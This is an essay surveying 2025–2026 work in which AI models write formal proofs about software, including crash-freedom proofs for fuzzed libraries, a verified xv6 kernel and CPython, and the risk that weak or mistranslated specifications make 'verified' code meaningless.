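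The agent wrote the specifications itself, and nobody reviewed them, so the proofs show that the interpreter matches the agent's reading of the manual. The finished program also passed 265 tests and ran for 12 hours of fuzzing without crashing. These results are useful evidence about the conversion to C++ and the 88 lines of unverified code around it, but a model wrote the tests too.

When Fang and Xiong repeated the task with Dafny, the agent wrote 2,070 lines and ran out of time before verifying them all. They attribute this to solver timeouts that gave the agent no useful feedback. One run with each tool isn't enough to show that Rocq suits agents better, and models in the 2025 benchmark did far better in Dafny than in Lean. The two results may be compatible, because the benchmark's tasks were small enough for a solver to settle most of the details, and its models saw the state of a Lean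 proof only five times per task. An agent that can check the proof state after every change benefits much more from a proof assistant.

A November 2026 study by Wesselink and colleagues shows that Dafny can also handle large proofs if somebody manages the solver carefully. Using Claude Opus 5 and 5.5, they verified 37 published algorithms, mostly for graphs, in more than 74,000 lines of Dafny. One was the Hopcroft–Tarjan triconnectivity test, which determines whether a network stays connected after the loss of any two nodes. They know of no earlier machine-checked proof of this test. The only algorithm they attempted but did not finish verifying was a related one that finds a network's triconnected components.

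The main difficulty was often solver timeouts rather than the mathematics. In a large method, the solver, Z3, receives so many facts at once that it runs out of time on claims it could otherwise prove. For the Lengauer–Tarjan algorithm, which analyses the possible paths through a program, the agent hid most definitions from Z3 and revealed each one only inside the small lemma that needed it. This removed all 36 timeouts in the main method and cut the solver's work by 93%.

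A person still reviewed the pseudocode and the contract for each algorithm before the agent began the proof, and Wesselink and colleagues acknowledge that an error missed at this stage could compromise the whole verification. How much people did after that varied. For Edmonds' blossom algorithm, which pairs up the nodes of a network, a person only chose the problem and monitored progress, though the agent could draw on an existing proof in another system. Other proofs stalled for weeks until somebody suggested a new approach or improved the tools.

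All 37 algorithms are well known, and the models had probably seen descriptions of them in training. A company's own code has no published correctness argument for a model to follow, and often no precise statement of what the code should do.

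## Machine-written proofs for real software, and their cost

The best-known proof about working software covers seL4, a microkernel (an operating-system kernel kept as small as possible). In 2009 it had 8,700 lines of C. Kleppmann (2025) writes in *Prediction* that proving it correct took 20 person-years and 200,000 lines in the proof assistant Isabelle. That is 23 lines of proof and half a working day for each line of C. *Machine-Generated Code Deserves Machine-Checked Proofs* reports that CompCert, a C compiler with a machine-checked proof, took about 3 person-years and 42,000 lines of Rocq.

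### Why few teams paid for proofs

Kleppmann argues that for most systems, bugs cost less than the proofs that would remove them. Users bear much of the cost of bugs, which gives developers less reason to pay for proofs. At seL4's rate, a 10,000-line web service would take 5,000 working days to verify, which would cost $4 million at $100 an hour. Few owners of such a service expect to lose that much to bugs. Even a company willing to pay would have trouble hiring people who can write such proofs. Kleppmann guesses that there are only a few hundred in the world.

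In December 2025, Kleppmann predicted that language models would make formal verification mainstream. They lower the price of verification because they can write the proofs, and a proof checker rejects any that are invalid. They also increase demand because all the code they generate has to be checked, and Kleppmann would rather have a proof than a human review. An expert still had to guide the model, but Kleppmann expected full automation within a few years. If the price of a proof fell a hundredfold, verifying the web service would cost $40,000, which a company might well pay for code that handles payments.

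A proof removes only the bugs that its specification covers, which weakens the comparison between the price of a proof and the price of bugs. Kleppmann expects writing specifications to become the hard part, which takes expertise but much less time than writing proofs by hand.

### Turning fuzz tests into theorems

Most existing software has no formal specification, but much of it has fuzz tests. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) describes a project that used these tests as specifications. Anthropic and Theorem, a startup that builds AI for program verification, had Claude prove security properties of 123 libraries from OSS-Fuzz, Google's service for fuzzing open-source software.

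A fuzz test has an entry point, which is a small function that takes a string of bytes and passes it to the library. Whoever wrote the entry point has in effect stated a property that the library should have, namely that no input makes it crash. A fuzzer checks this property only for the inputs it tries. The project turned it into a theorem about a compiled program *P*:

For every input *x* smaller than 64 MB, *P* exits normally on *x*, without a crash, a memory-safety error or a failed assertion.

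The number of such inputs has more than 150 million digits, so no amount of testing could cover them. Claude proved the theorem for 239 entry points in a few weeks, according to EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026). The work on each entry point went roughly as follows:

1. A compiler turned the entry point and the library into one program for RISC-V, a processor design with a fairly simple instruction set.
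2. Software converted the fuzz test into a precise property of that program, written in Rocq.
3. Claude wrote a proof of the property.
4. Rocq's kernel checked the proof.

Since the theorem is about machine code, it holds even if the compiler made a mistake. It also applies to existing C libraries without requiring them to be rewritten in a language designed for verification. But the proof has to account for every instruction. OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026) reports that Claude wrote about 600,000 lines of Rocq for a program with 18,000 instructions. *Claude Writes 180 Million Lines of Proofs* (Smith, 2026) gives a total of 180 million lines for the project.

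The seL4 team wrote about 10,000 lines of proof per person-year, so Claude's 180 million lines would have taken them 18,000 person-years. That comparison overstates the achievement, because the seL4 proof covers what the kernel does, while most of Claude's lines show only that a program doesn't crash. Proofs about machine code are also long because they include details that a proof about C can leave to the compiler. The length matters less than it would for ordinary code, because nobody has to read a proof that Rocq has checked.

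### What happens when a proof gets stuck

Suppose a library has this function, and a fuzz test passes its input straight to it. The first byte of a message gives the number of bytes that follow, and the function adds those bytes up:

```
unsigned checksum(const uint8_t *data, size_t size) {
    if (size == 0) return 0;
    size_t n = data[0];
    unsigned sum = 0;
    for (size_t i = 1; i <= n; i++)
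        sum += data[i];
    return sum;
}
```

To prove that the function never reads outside the message, Claude would have to show that *i* < *size* whenever the program reads `data[i]`. The available facts are that *size* is at least 1, *i* is between 1 and *n*, and *n* is at most 255. None of these facts relates *n* to *size*, so Claude can't complete the proof from them.

There are two possible reasons. Every caller might already have checked the length, in which case the code is fine and the proof only needs that fact as a precondition. Here the caller is the fuzz test, which checks nothing, so the missing fact leads directly to an input that breaks the function. A message consisting of the single byte 1 has *size* = 1 and *n* = 1, and the loop reads `data[1]`, just past the end. The repair is one line after the declaration of `n`:

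`if (n >= size) return 0;`

Now *i* ≤ *n* and *n* < *size*, so *i* < *size* and the proof goes through.

A fuzzer would find this bug almost immediately. It would have much more trouble if the loop ran only for messages whose first four bytes matched a checksum of the rest, because a random message would pass that check about once in four billion attempts. Keeping inputs that reach new code wouldn't help much, since a nearly correct checksum reaches no new code. The proof fails at the same place however rare the input is.

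OpenNET reports that Claude found and fixed hundreds of bugs that fuzzing had missed. One, CVE-2026-56132, was a buffer overflow in libexpat, a widely used library for reading XML files. Because fuzzers had already tested all the affected libraries, these bugs are better evidence for the method than the number of lines of proof.

A patch written by Claude is untrusted output. The theorem confirms that the patched program doesn't crash, but it would also hold for a patch that rejected every message. A maintainer still has to review the patch and run the library's functional tests. The theorem also doesn't apply to the version people download until the maintainer accepts the patch.

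According to EconoTimes, the published material includes proofs for programs that needed no changes and specifications for programs that Claude couldn't prove. Publishing the unproved specifications is useful because other teams can try to prove them with newer models, and a failed proof may be due to a bug.

### The limits of the library proofs

The theorem covers one modelled machine, where each program runs in a single thread on a simplified version of Linux, with a fixed amount of memory and all the library code it needs built in. OpenNET lists threads, dynamic linking and misbehaving hardware among the remaining risks. Most Linux software uses dynamic linking, which means that it loads shared libraries when it starts.

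*Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification* (Leip, 2026) quotes Anthropic's acknowledgement that most people run these libraries on x86 or ARM processors and link them dynamically to glibc, the usual C library on Linux. The project used RISC-V and musl, a simpler C library. A missing length check in the C code would normally cause problems on every processor, so the RISC-V proof is good evidence about the x86 version. But it doesn't prove the x86 version correct, because the machine code is different and may use separate routines written for that processor.

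The theorem also covers only the code that the chosen entry points can reach. A function that no fuzz test calls may still crash. A reader told that a library is "verified" could easily miss this, so it helps to ask which entry points and which version the proof covers.

Two other parts of the project covered more than crashes. Claude proved that the Linux kernel's code for zlib, a common compression format, follows the format's published standard. It also wrote an interpreter in Rust for part of the Python language and used Verus to prove that the interpreter follows a formal description of Python's behaviour. To check that description, the team ran more than 1.7 million random programs in both the new interpreter and CPython, the standard implementation of Python. The results agreed in 99.95% of cases, and OpenNET says the remaining programs, roughly 850, were known edge cases.

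### An operating system, down to the instructions

In *Extending concurrent separation logic to the hardware level*, the MIT researchers Kaashoek and Zeldovich (2026) proved much more about a single program when they verified xv6, a small Unix-like teaching operating system, with proofs that Claude Code helped write. (Zeldovich also worked on the Anthropic project.) The kernel has 6,657 lines of C and assembly, which compile to 8,725 instructions. The proofs of the kernel and several small programs that run on it total about 1.6 million lines of Rocq.

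Kernels are hard to verify because so much happens at once. In the model, eight processor cores run xv6 while the disk writes to memory on its own, devices interrupt the cores, and the power can fail at any moment. The theorem requires the kernel's invariants to hold through every possible ordering of these events. This implies, for example, that an ordinary program can't corrupt the kernel's memory and that a power failure leaves the file system consistent.

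A second theorem describes what a user sees. If somebody types `echo hello world`, the system can print only `hello world` or one of a few listed errors, such as a message that it couldn't start `echo`. The proof relies on results about the compiled kernel, shell and `echo` program.

Both theorems restrict what the system may do but don't require it to do anything. A computer that never printed a character would satisfy the theorem about `echo`. Kaashoek and Zeldovich point out that anyone can rule this out by running xv6 and typing the command. They also didn't prove that the kernel keeps one process from learning another's data, which many users would want from an operating system.

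The work uncovered 11 bugs in xv6, some of which could crash it. The project took 102 days, including building a framework for such proofs. The process was far from automatic. The agents did the tedious reasoning about instructions, but the researchers laid out the overall plan, helped design the intermediate specifications, and wrote prompts that added up to about three times the length of their paper.

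### An ordinary x86 program

In mid-September 2026, the security company Zellic and its partner V12 started a formal verification project for the processors and C library that most Linux servers use. They published their first results, with proofs in Lean, on 30 October. One theorem covers runs of a single program from the moment Linux starts it until it exits.

Much of the difficulty lies in code the programmer never wrote. Before a plain C program's own code starts, glibc on x86 runs about ten times as many distinct instructions as musl does on RISC-V. glibc also picks routines optimised for the processor. On the processor Zellic used, its string-comparison routine has 316 instructions and 45 jumps, compared with 14 and 4 for musl's on RISC-V. Any proof about the program has to cover the glibc routine, because glibc calls it during startup.

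The theorem guarantees that every run that reaches the program's main function ends in a specified way. A run may crash during start-up, but the theorem restricts what it can print before that. The theorem holds only if the processor matches the one in Zellic's test machine, nothing outside interferes with the process, and Linux grants its memory requests. This is a much smaller result than the proofs for 123 libraries, but it shows that the same approach can work on the more complicated machines that people actually use.

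### A copy of Python

Andrews and Zhang's *Formalizing CPython* (2026) used proofs mainly to look for bugs. Claude Opus 5.5 rewrote CPython functions in Lean, line by line. Each copy had to match real Python on at least 50,000 tricky inputs before an agent tried to prove anything about it. For example, CPython has a fast function for computing the length of a `range`, such as the numbers from 0 to 10 in steps of 2, and a slower one for very large numbers. One proof shows that both always give the correct count.

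By November 2026 the copy had 613,318 lines of Lean, and 4,071 functions had passed review by a second agent. That is about 16% of CPython. The work produced 418 bug reports. Most were minor, but about 55 of the bugs can crash Python or corrupt its memory when it runs ordinary Python code.

The proofs are about the Lean copy, and only tests connect the copy to the C code that people run. In the copy of one JSON routine, for example, every request for memory succeeds, but on a real computer such requests can fail. Andrews and Zhang therefore also run every accepted statement against real Python, which has caught several statements that were validly proved about the copy but wrong about the real program.

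In the file that implements Python's types, the reviewing agent accepted none of the 142 functions in the first round of review and had accepted 135 after five. Many early proofs were correct but useless. One showed that if a function returns a number, the number is at least zero, which is also true of a function that always crashes.

### What each project proved

A fifth project, from Google DeepMind, went beyond crashes to the security of a messaging protocol. *AlphaProof Code* (Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues, 2026) describes agents that proved properties of libsignal, the code behind the encrypted messenger Signal, as compiled for ARM processors. One is forward secrecy, which means an attacker who steals today's keys can't read earlier messages. The proofs cover a small test program for one-to-one conversations, not the whole library, according to *Google DeepMind Uses AlphaProof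 Code to Verify a Compiled Signal Harness* (EconoTimes, 2026).

| Software | What the proof covers | Form of the code | Main gap |
|---|---|---|---|
| 123 libraries | No crash on inputs under 64 MB, from 239 entry points | RISC-V machine code | Most users run other processors |
| xv6 | Kernel invariants, and the output of a few commands | RISC-V machine code | No guarantee that any output appears |
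| One x86 program | How every run that reaches the main function ends | x86 machine code | One program on one processor model |
| CPython | Chosen properties of 4,071 functions | A copy in Lean | Only tests link the copy to the original |
| libsignal | Secrecy and authentication between two people | ARM machine code | A small test program, not the whole library |

All five can be called "verified", but ranking them by size would be a mistake. The libsignal proof covers properties its users care about directly, while the library proofs rule out one class of failure in much more software. The library approach is probably the easiest for a team to copy on its own code, since it may already have the fuzz tests.

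Equivalence proofs are another option when software has no specification. Fonseca mentions in *Full-stack verification is the new trend* that the company Harmonic used its agent Aristotle to prove that a faster version of a C library for large-number arithmetic gives the same results as the original. The old code serves as the specification, so nobody has to write one, but the faster version will also reproduce any mistake in the old results.

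### How far the price has fallen

| Project | Code | Lines of proof | Reported effort |
|---|---|---|---|
| seL4, 2009 | 8,700 lines of C | 200,000 | 20 person-years |
| xv6, 2026 | 6,657 lines of C and assembly | 1.6 million | 102 days |
| 123 libraries, 2026 | 239 entry points | 180 million | A few weeks |

Effort for the two newer projects is given in calendar time, so it can't be compared directly with person-years. For xv6, the total was roughly 204 person-days at most, assuming both researchers worked on it every day. That is about 0.03 person-days per line of code, a sixteenth of the half person-day per line that seL4 took. The xv6 and seL4 theorems differ, and both xv6 researchers are experts, so an ordinary team shouldn't expect the same rate.

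Theorem reports a much larger saving on another task. In February 2026 it said that its AI had translated all 1,276 statements of a textbook on formal proof from Rocq to Lean with about 2 person-days of human work. The company estimates that people would have needed 2.75 person-years, about 350 times as long. But Theorem sells verification, and a textbook is easier to translate than a working library because its authors have already stated every theorem precisely.

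These comparisons also leave out the cost of computing, which offsets some of the savings in labour. Keles (2026), in *Formal Verification is Not Verifiable*, puts Claude's output in the Anthropic project at a billion lines of Rocq. If that figure includes failed attempts, Claude discarded more than four lines for each one it kept. Maintenance will also cost money, because each new version of a library compiles to different machine code and needs a new or repaired proof. Agents can probably do most of that work, but a project that releases weekly updates would have to pay for it each time.

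Kleppmann's prediction has held up well on price. Keles, who made a similar prediction in December 2025, now considers formal verification mainstream, citing the number of new companies and the leaders of coding-agent teams who discuss it. This is good evidence of interest, but weaker evidence that ordinary teams prove their own code correct. The projects described here came from an AI company, a university, a security firm, a pair of researchers and Google.

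The UK's Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA), a public funder of high-risk research, is also trying to make proofs cheaper through its Safeguarded AI programme. In the programme's thesis of May 2026, Ammann (2026) writes that AI agents now produce more software in an hour than human teams used to write in months, and that the ability to check it has not kept up. The programme aims to close this gap by using AI to build mathematical models and prove things about them, and to make verification faster and more widely applicable.

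Ammann expects the same gap to appear in science, engineering and decision making. Proofs will be harder to apply there than in software. A processor has a manual that defines each instruction, so a team can build a fairly accurate model of it. No such manual exists for a power grid or a hospital, and relying on a proof about a poor model of either could be worse than having no proof.

The human work of deciding what to prove has shrunk least. Tolmach and Klaus (2026), in *The proof is in the spec*, describe how Boris Cherny, who leads Claude Code at Anthropic, used a couple of short prompts to have Claude formalise one of the company's code libraries and got 16 sets of bug fixes. Tolmach and Klaus, who work for a verification company, accept that the bugs were real but say that such a run doesn't yet establish that the code is correct. They think the bottleneck is now choosing the specification,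 the model and the assumptions.

People don't need to read the Signal project's 6.5 million lines of proof, but they do have to make sure the specifications and processor rules it depends on are right. Those run to about 26,000 lines, three times the length of seL4's C code.

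## When the specification is weak or wrong

A proof checker confirms that a program meets its specification, but it doesn't check that the specification asks for the right thing. Suppose a generator has to write a function that returns the largest number in a list. It produces this Dafny method, adapted from an example in *Verified But Vacuous* (Vempaty, Sompalle and colleagues, 2026):

```
method Max(a: seq<int>) returns (m: int)
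  requires |a| > 0
  ensures m >= 0
{
  m := 0;
}
```

The method returns 0 for the list [5, 3, 7]. Dafny accepts the method because the contract requires only a non-negative result.

### What a postcondition has to do

A postcondition must accept every correct output and reject every wrong one. The postcondition `m >= 0` accepts the wrong output 0 for [5, 3, 7] and rejects the correct output −1 for [−3, −1]. Dafny would therefore reject every correct program for this task and accept one that always returns 0.

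Let *I* be the set of input-output pairs that the user would accept, and *S* the set that the specification accepts. In *Verus-SpecGym*, Agarwal, Neamtu and colleagues (2026) call a specification sound if *S* ⊆ *I* and complete if *I* ⊆ *S*. A wrong program can pass if the specification isn't sound, and a correct program may fail if it isn't complete. A failed proof prompts somebody to investigate, but a postcondition that is too weak makes the proof easier, so nothing draws attention to it.

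The table shows which outputs some possible postconditions accept for the list [5, 3, 7]:

| Postcondition | 7 (right) | 5 | 0 | 100 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `m` is not negative | Accepts | Accepts | Accepts | Accepts |
| `m` is at least as large as every element | Accepts | Rejects | Rejects | Accepts |
| `m` is in the list | Accepts | Accepts | Rejects | Rejects |
| `m` is in the list and at least as large as every element | Accepts | Rejects | Rejects | Rejects |

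The last version is right for every list, because only the largest number meets both conditions. It is easy to leave out "is in the list". *VerusEval* (Wang, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) reports the same mistake in a generated contract for a function that returns the shortest list in a collection. The contract fixed the length of the result but didn't require the result to come from the collection, so for the lists [1, 2] and [3] it allowed the answer [9].

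Preconditions can be wrong too. Agarwal and colleagues give the example of finding the first position of a number in a sorted array. A precondition that requires each element to be strictly larger than the one before it excludes [10, 20, 20, 20, 30], so a proof would not cover arrays with repeated values. If the precondition doesn't require the array to be sorted, a correct binary search can't be verified, because binary search doesn't work on unsorted arrays.

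### Verified programs with almost nothing to prove

Vempaty and colleagues measured how much verification guarantees about a program. They rebuilt a pipeline that Li, Zetzsche and Somayyajula published in 2025, in which a model writes Dafny code, the verifier checks it and a compiler turns it into Python. Claude Opus 4.7 made ten attempts at each of the 164 HumanEval problems, and Dafny accepted 99.1% of the programs. Of the accepted programs, 94.7% had no postcondition, 3.4% had one that didn't refer to the separate specification, and 1.9% had one that did.

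Without a postcondition, Dafny still proves that a program terminates and never reads outside an array, but it proves nothing about the answer. The prompt is a plausible cause of the missing postconditions. Its worked example contains a method with no postcondition and a list of expected results. Dafny assumes these results during verification and checks them only when the program runs. Most of the programs did work, but the evidence for that comes from HumanEval's basic tests, which 92.6% of all attempts passed. "99.1% verified" does not mean that 99.1% were proved correct.

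On two harder sets of problems, Dafny accepted 97.2% and 92.2% of programs, but only 2.7% and 2.3% of the accepted programs referred to the specification. A program counts as referring to the specification if at least one postcondition names a predicate or function from the specification file. Checking this takes less than a hundredth of a second.

Vempaty and colleagues stress that this checks only form. The postcondition `r == 2 * x` fully specifies a function that doubles a number, but it fails the check because it names nothing from the specification file. A named predicate that is always true passes. The share of HumanEval programs with a meaningful postcondition could therefore be higher or lower than 1.9%, but it can't exceed 5.3%, the share with any postcondition.

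In their own pipeline, one agent writes the specification, another writes the code, and the software rejects any program that fails verification. They ran it on two sets of Rust problems. Of the verified programs, 11.5% (124 of 1,080) failed hidden tests on one set and 14.8% (229 of 1,545) on the other. Weak specifications are one likely cause, but problems in the translation from Dafny to Rust or in the tests could also explain the failures.

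On the second set, Vempaty and colleagues also tested the specifications directly with Post2Exe, which turns a postcondition into a runnable check and tries it on right and wrong outputs. Of the 1,316 verified programs that had passed the hidden tests, only 535 (40.7%) had specifications that also passed these checks. In most cases, the code seemed right but the specification didn't fully describe the task. Proving code against such a specification adds less assurance beyond the tests than the word "verified" suggests.

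### How well models write specifications

Agarwal and colleagues gave six models 581 problems from the programming-contest site Codeforces and asked for Verus specifications instead of solutions. Codeforces contestants can try to find inputs that make each other's solutions fail, which gave the researchers realistic wrong outputs. A specification counted as correct only if it classified every test correctly.

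Gemini 3.1 Pro succeeded on 77.8% of the problems, GPT-5.3 Codex on 57.8% and Claude Opus 4.6 on 51.1%. Three open models scored between 21.5% and 25.5%. If the researchers had tested only whether specifications accept valid inputs and right outputs, and not whether they reject wrong outputs, GPT-5.3 Codex would have scored 76.6% instead of 57.8%.

Writing a specification was often harder for a model than solving the problem. Agarwal and colleagues found that GPT-5.3 Codex wrote a correct Python program for 153 of 187 problems for which it had written a wrong specification. It was also unreliable at checking its own specifications, approving 49 of 191 that the tests had shown to be wrong.

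Wang and colleagues examined 13,716 generated Verus files from four systems and five models. Only 42.3% of the files that Verus accepted passed three further checks, which looked for trivial contracts, tried sample inputs and outputs, and compared each contract with a reference. Systems with higher acceptance rates did not consistently write more correct contracts, so ranking systems by acceptance rate can favor those that write loose contracts.

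### False claims that become provable

Researchers have studied the same translation problem in mathematics, where a model turns an ordinary sentence into a formal statement. Cornish, Ghinassi and colleagues (2026), in *FaithformBench*, tested what happens when the sentence is wrong. One test claimed that if 3^*x* = 5, then 3^(*x*+2) = 51. The right answer is 45, since 3^(*x*+2) is 9 times 3^*x*. A model called Kimina translated the claim into Lean like this:

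```
theorem step (x : ℕ) (h : 3^x = 5) : 3^(x+2) = 51
```

The symbol ℕ makes *x* a natural number, but no natural number satisfies 3^*x* = 5, because 3¹ is 3 and 3² is 9. The hypothesis is therefore impossible, so anything follows from it, including the false claim. When the sentence contained the correct 45, Kimina made *x* a real number, as it should be.

Cornish and colleagues call it silent correction when a translation turns a false claim into a true formal statement. They took 12,784 reasoning steps from solutions that experts had marked correct, had a model plant an error in each, and tried to prove the translations of the altered steps. All four models trained specifically for translation into Lean often turned false claims into provable statements. Goedel, the best of them on correct claims, did so most often on the three harder sets of problems. A likely reason is that training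 rewards provable statements. Four general-purpose models, including Claude Opus 4.7, turned false claims into provable statements much less often.

The method gives only a lower bound on translation errors. A system that translated every true claim as 0 = 0 and every false one as 0 = 1 would get a perfect score.

Human judgments show a similar pattern. *LeanSide* (2026), a system that checks students' proofs, translates each step into Lean. Experts found that it misrepresented 18 of 1,038 correct steps but 22 of 117 incorrect ones. In 12 cases, a student had made a small slip, such as multiplying matrices of incompatible sizes. Lean wouldn't compile the faithful translation, so LeanSide corrected the mistake to get a valid statement. A tool that turns a developer's requirements into a specification could hide a contradiction in the same way.

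*Beyond Compilation* (Zhang, Gallardo Candela and colleagues, 2026) measured how often translated statements compile without being faithful to the original. An agent based on GPT-5.2 translated 227 statements from university textbooks. Of the translations, 87.2% compiled, but two AI judges accepted only 57.7% as faithful. Human reviewers checked every rejection and confirmed most, so real errors account for at least 23.8 percentage points of the 29.5-point gap. Tolmach and Klaus quote figures from an earlier version of the paper, 89.5% and 60.5%.

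Feedback from Lean's compiler raised the share of statements that compiled by 49.3 percentage points on average, but the share judged faithful by only 27.2. An agent that keeps editing until the error messages stop may change the statement's meaning.

Newer models do much better. GPT-5.2, acting as the only judge, accepted 83% of the translations by GPT-6 Astra and by Claude Opus 5.5, which each had one attempt and no tools. Other AI models and Opus 5.5 itself reviewed the 54 rejections and classed only 4 as translation errors. The models may have seen these textbooks in training, and nobody reviewed the accepted translations. Still, translating a self-contained mathematical statement is probably no longer a major weakness of the best models.

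### Models that describe the wrong system

A team that wants to prove something about an existing system often starts with a formal model of its behavior. *SysMoBench* (2025) tests whether AI can write such models in TLA+, a language that companies such as Amazon and Microsoft use to specify systems with many interacting parts. In *Can LLMs model real world systems in TLA+*, published by SIGOPS, the benchmark's designers describe an early failure. They asked Claude for a model of etcd, a database that uses the Raft protocol to keep its copies consistent. The model passed the basic checks, but it was essentially the specification from the appendix of the original Raft paper and had little to do with etcd's code.

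The benchmark covers eleven systems. To test whether a TLA+ model conforms to the code, it records real runs and splits them into steps, each with a starting state, an action and a resulting state. It then checks whether the model allows each step. In May 2026 the leading AI models scored near 100% on syntax, but averaged only about 46% on conformance and 41% on the properties the system should always have.

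Claude Sonnet made such an error when modeling ZooKeeper, a service that coordinates groups of servers. When a server changes its vote in a leadership election, ZooKeeper overwrites the old vote. The model kept both, as many textbook examples do, so its votes could add up to a result that the real system would never reach. A valid theorem about that model might therefore not apply to ZooKeeper.

The designers have since built a specialised agent, Specula, which gets full marks for conformance and properties on the current tasks. The conformance score covers only behaviour that occurred in the recorded runs. In one test, the recorded runs never used one of the lock operations, so the check could not cover it.

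### Testing a specification

The easiest test checks for contracts that mean nothing. Wang and colleagues use the verifier to try to prove that a precondition is always false or that a postcondition is always true. If either proof succeeds, the contract is worthless. This would catch a precondition like 3^*x* = 5 for a natural number *x*, but not the postcondition `m >= 0`, which excludes some outputs.

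The next step is to run the postcondition on right and wrong outputs, as in the table for [5, 3, 7]. The wrong outputs should be nearly right. *SpecRL* (2026) has a model propose plausible mistakes, such as answers that are off by one, and measures the share that the specification rejects. The results can also guide repairs. In *Automatic Generation of Formal Specification and Verification Annotations Using LLMs* (2026), four Dafny programs had preconditions that were too weak or postconditions that were too strong. Claude Opus 4.5 corrected all four when shown which tests had exposed the problem.

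Such tests cover only the cases somebody tried. In Wang and colleagues' experiment, they rejected 23.6% of the accepted files. Of the files that passed, Verus could prove only 63.2% equivalent to the reference contract. The rest may still be correct, because a failed proof doesn't show that two contracts differ, and the reference itself may contain a mistake. The researchers selected 61 of the 762 reference contracts for closer review and found probable defects in 36. After they restored a missing guarantee in one reference, 10 of the 11 generated contracts that had failed against it turned out to be equivalent.

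Models are poor at working out the expected outputs for tests. *Judging Is Not Enumerating* (Chen, Chen and colleagues, 2026) found that test suites written by models accepted only 19–42% of correct programs, often because the models had invented requirements. The models did choose useful inputs. When the researchers took the expected outputs from a trusted program instead, the suites still caught 94% of wrong programs. A team without a trusted program can at least discard any suite that rejects a solution it knows to be correct.

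Another way to test a specification is to plant faults in the code and check whether it still verifies. In the `Max` method, a tool might change `m := 0` to `m := 1`. Dafny accepts the new version too, which suggests that the postcondition is too weak. In *MutDafny*, Amaral and Mendes (2025) built a tool that plants 40 kinds of fault and tried it on 794 real Dafny programs. They examined some of the undetected faults by hand and found five weak specifications, about one for every 241 lines of code.

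A fault-planting score ranks specifications but doesn't show what to fix. *Spec-Harness* (2026) describes a Java method that swaps the case of a letter and leaves other characters alone. A model wrote a specification that only required a lowercase letter to become some capital letter, so "a" could become "Z". The specification also excluded valid inputs such as "~", so it needed both a stronger postcondition and a weaker precondition. A planted fault can also break the proof for an unrelated reason, which inflates the specification's score. In one case even an empty specification scored above zero.

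### Separate authors

A generator that writes both the code and the specification can make the proof succeed by weakening the specification. Having separate agents write the two removes the incentive to do this, but it doesn't help if both misread the request in the same way. Vempaty and colleagues' second pipeline separates the two jobs but uses Claude Opus 4.7 for both, and at least 11% of its verified programs still failed hidden tests. Tests that models write for faulty code can repeat the code's misreading, so writing the specification before any code exists may also help. A person or a different model would probably be a better second author than the same model, though these experiments don't measure how much either would help.

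### Specifications that a user can read

Councilman, Fu and colleagues (2025), in *Towards Formal Verification of LLM-Generated Code from Natural Language Prompts*, argue that the user has to check the specification, because only the user knows what they wanted. Most users can't read Dafny or Lean. The researchers therefore designed a formal language that resembles English, for people who use Ansible, a tool for configuring servers. A request to install the zsh command shell and make it a user's default looks like this:

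`install zsh; set default shell for user="dev" to zsh`

Their system, Astrogator, compares a generated Ansible program with such a query. It takes details such as package names from a hand-built reference list, so the user doesn't need to know that the numerical library numpy is called `python3-numpy` on Debian Linux.

The wording of a query can also expose an ambiguity in the instruction. "Copy a file from /path/a to /path/b" could mean copying within the remote server or from the user's own machine. The researchers meant copying within the server, but all six models they tried wrote code to copy from the user's machine. A query that states where each path is gives the user a chance to notice the mismatch.

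The six models wrote 1,260 programs for 21 tasks, and 334 of the programs were correct. Astrogator accepted 83% of the correct programs and rejected 92% of the incorrect ones. Of the programs it accepted, 79.8% were correct, compared with 26.5% of all the programs.

Of the 70 incorrect programs that Astrogator accepted, 61 would have worked under assumptions that didn't hold on the test machines, such as the existence of a certain user account. Astrogator can list these assumptions for the user to confirm, but in the experiment they were accepted automatically. Seven others did something extra and unwanted. For example, some overwrote a file that they should have created only if it was missing, because the query didn't specify what to do if the file existed.

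The researchers wrote the queries themselves, so the experiment doesn't show whether ordinary users would spot a wrong one. They also doubt the approach would extend to general-purpose languages such as Python, where a readable query language would either leave out too much or fill up with technical detail.

### What it takes to review a short statement

Dalal describes a review of this kind in *An Experiment in Formal Verification with Claude*. The company Succinct had written a paper on VEIL, a method for adding privacy to cryptographic proofs, with about 30 pages of new arguments that nobody outside the company had reviewed. Claude Opus 4.6 and 4.7 wrote the theorem statements, definitions and proofs in Lean, and people reviewed the statements and definitions.

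The human work took about one to two times as long as writing the paper, whereas formalising by hand often takes ten times as long. Most of that time went into the statements and definitions, which needed dozens of rounds of revision and can run to a thousand lines of Lean for a full protocol. The work also exposed an error in the paper, which claimed a slightly stronger privacy guarantee than one protocol gave.

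Some of Claude's mistakes were easy to overlook. It repeatedly swapped "for every" and "there is", which can make a statement trivially true. For example, "there is an element at least as large as every element" describes the maximum of a list, but "for every element, there is an element at least as large" is true of any list, because each element is as large as itself. *The Faithfulness Gap* (2026) shows how the same swap turns a well-known theorem about maximum values into a trivial statement that Lean accepts. Claude also assumed that attackers had less information than real ones would, which makes a security theorem easier to prove but less useful.

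Claude does not seem to have exploited these mistakes. When an error had weakened a theorem, Claude still proved the stronger version from the paper. Dalal nevertheless recommends that people write the statements and definitions by hand and leave only the proofs to the model. The team found most of the problems only after building a tool that displayed the Lean code next to the English text.

### Is a specification easier to review than code?

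Dalal found that checking Claude's statements was much easier than checking every argument in the paper. The same can be true of code. For example, two short conditions define the maximum of a list, however complicated the program that computes it, and they stay the same when somebody replaces that program with a faster one.

Haskell for all's *A sufficiently detailed spec is code* (2026) disputes the assumption that a specification is simpler than the corresponding code. The objection holds for much everyday software. If a shop's delivery charge depends on weight, postcode and a dozen special offers, a complete specification has to list all the same details as the program, so a reviewer would have about as much to read and could miss the same mistakes.

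A reply, *A sufficiently comprehensive spec is not (necessarily) code*, points out that many different programs can satisfy one specification. The specification is sufficient if its author would accept any of them. Writing a specification also forces decisions that are easy to miss in code. For example, before proving anything about a queue shared by several threads, Tolmach and Klaus would decide whether items must leave in the order they arrived and whether a memory request can fail.

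A short specification can still be hard to judge. Zhang and colleagues asked human reviewers whether 69 disputed Lean translations matched their textbook statements. Each translation was a single theorem, yet any two reviewers agreed on only 70–75% of them. These cases were unusually hard, but the reviewers had the intended meaning in front of them, and a team reviewing a specification for new software often doesn't.

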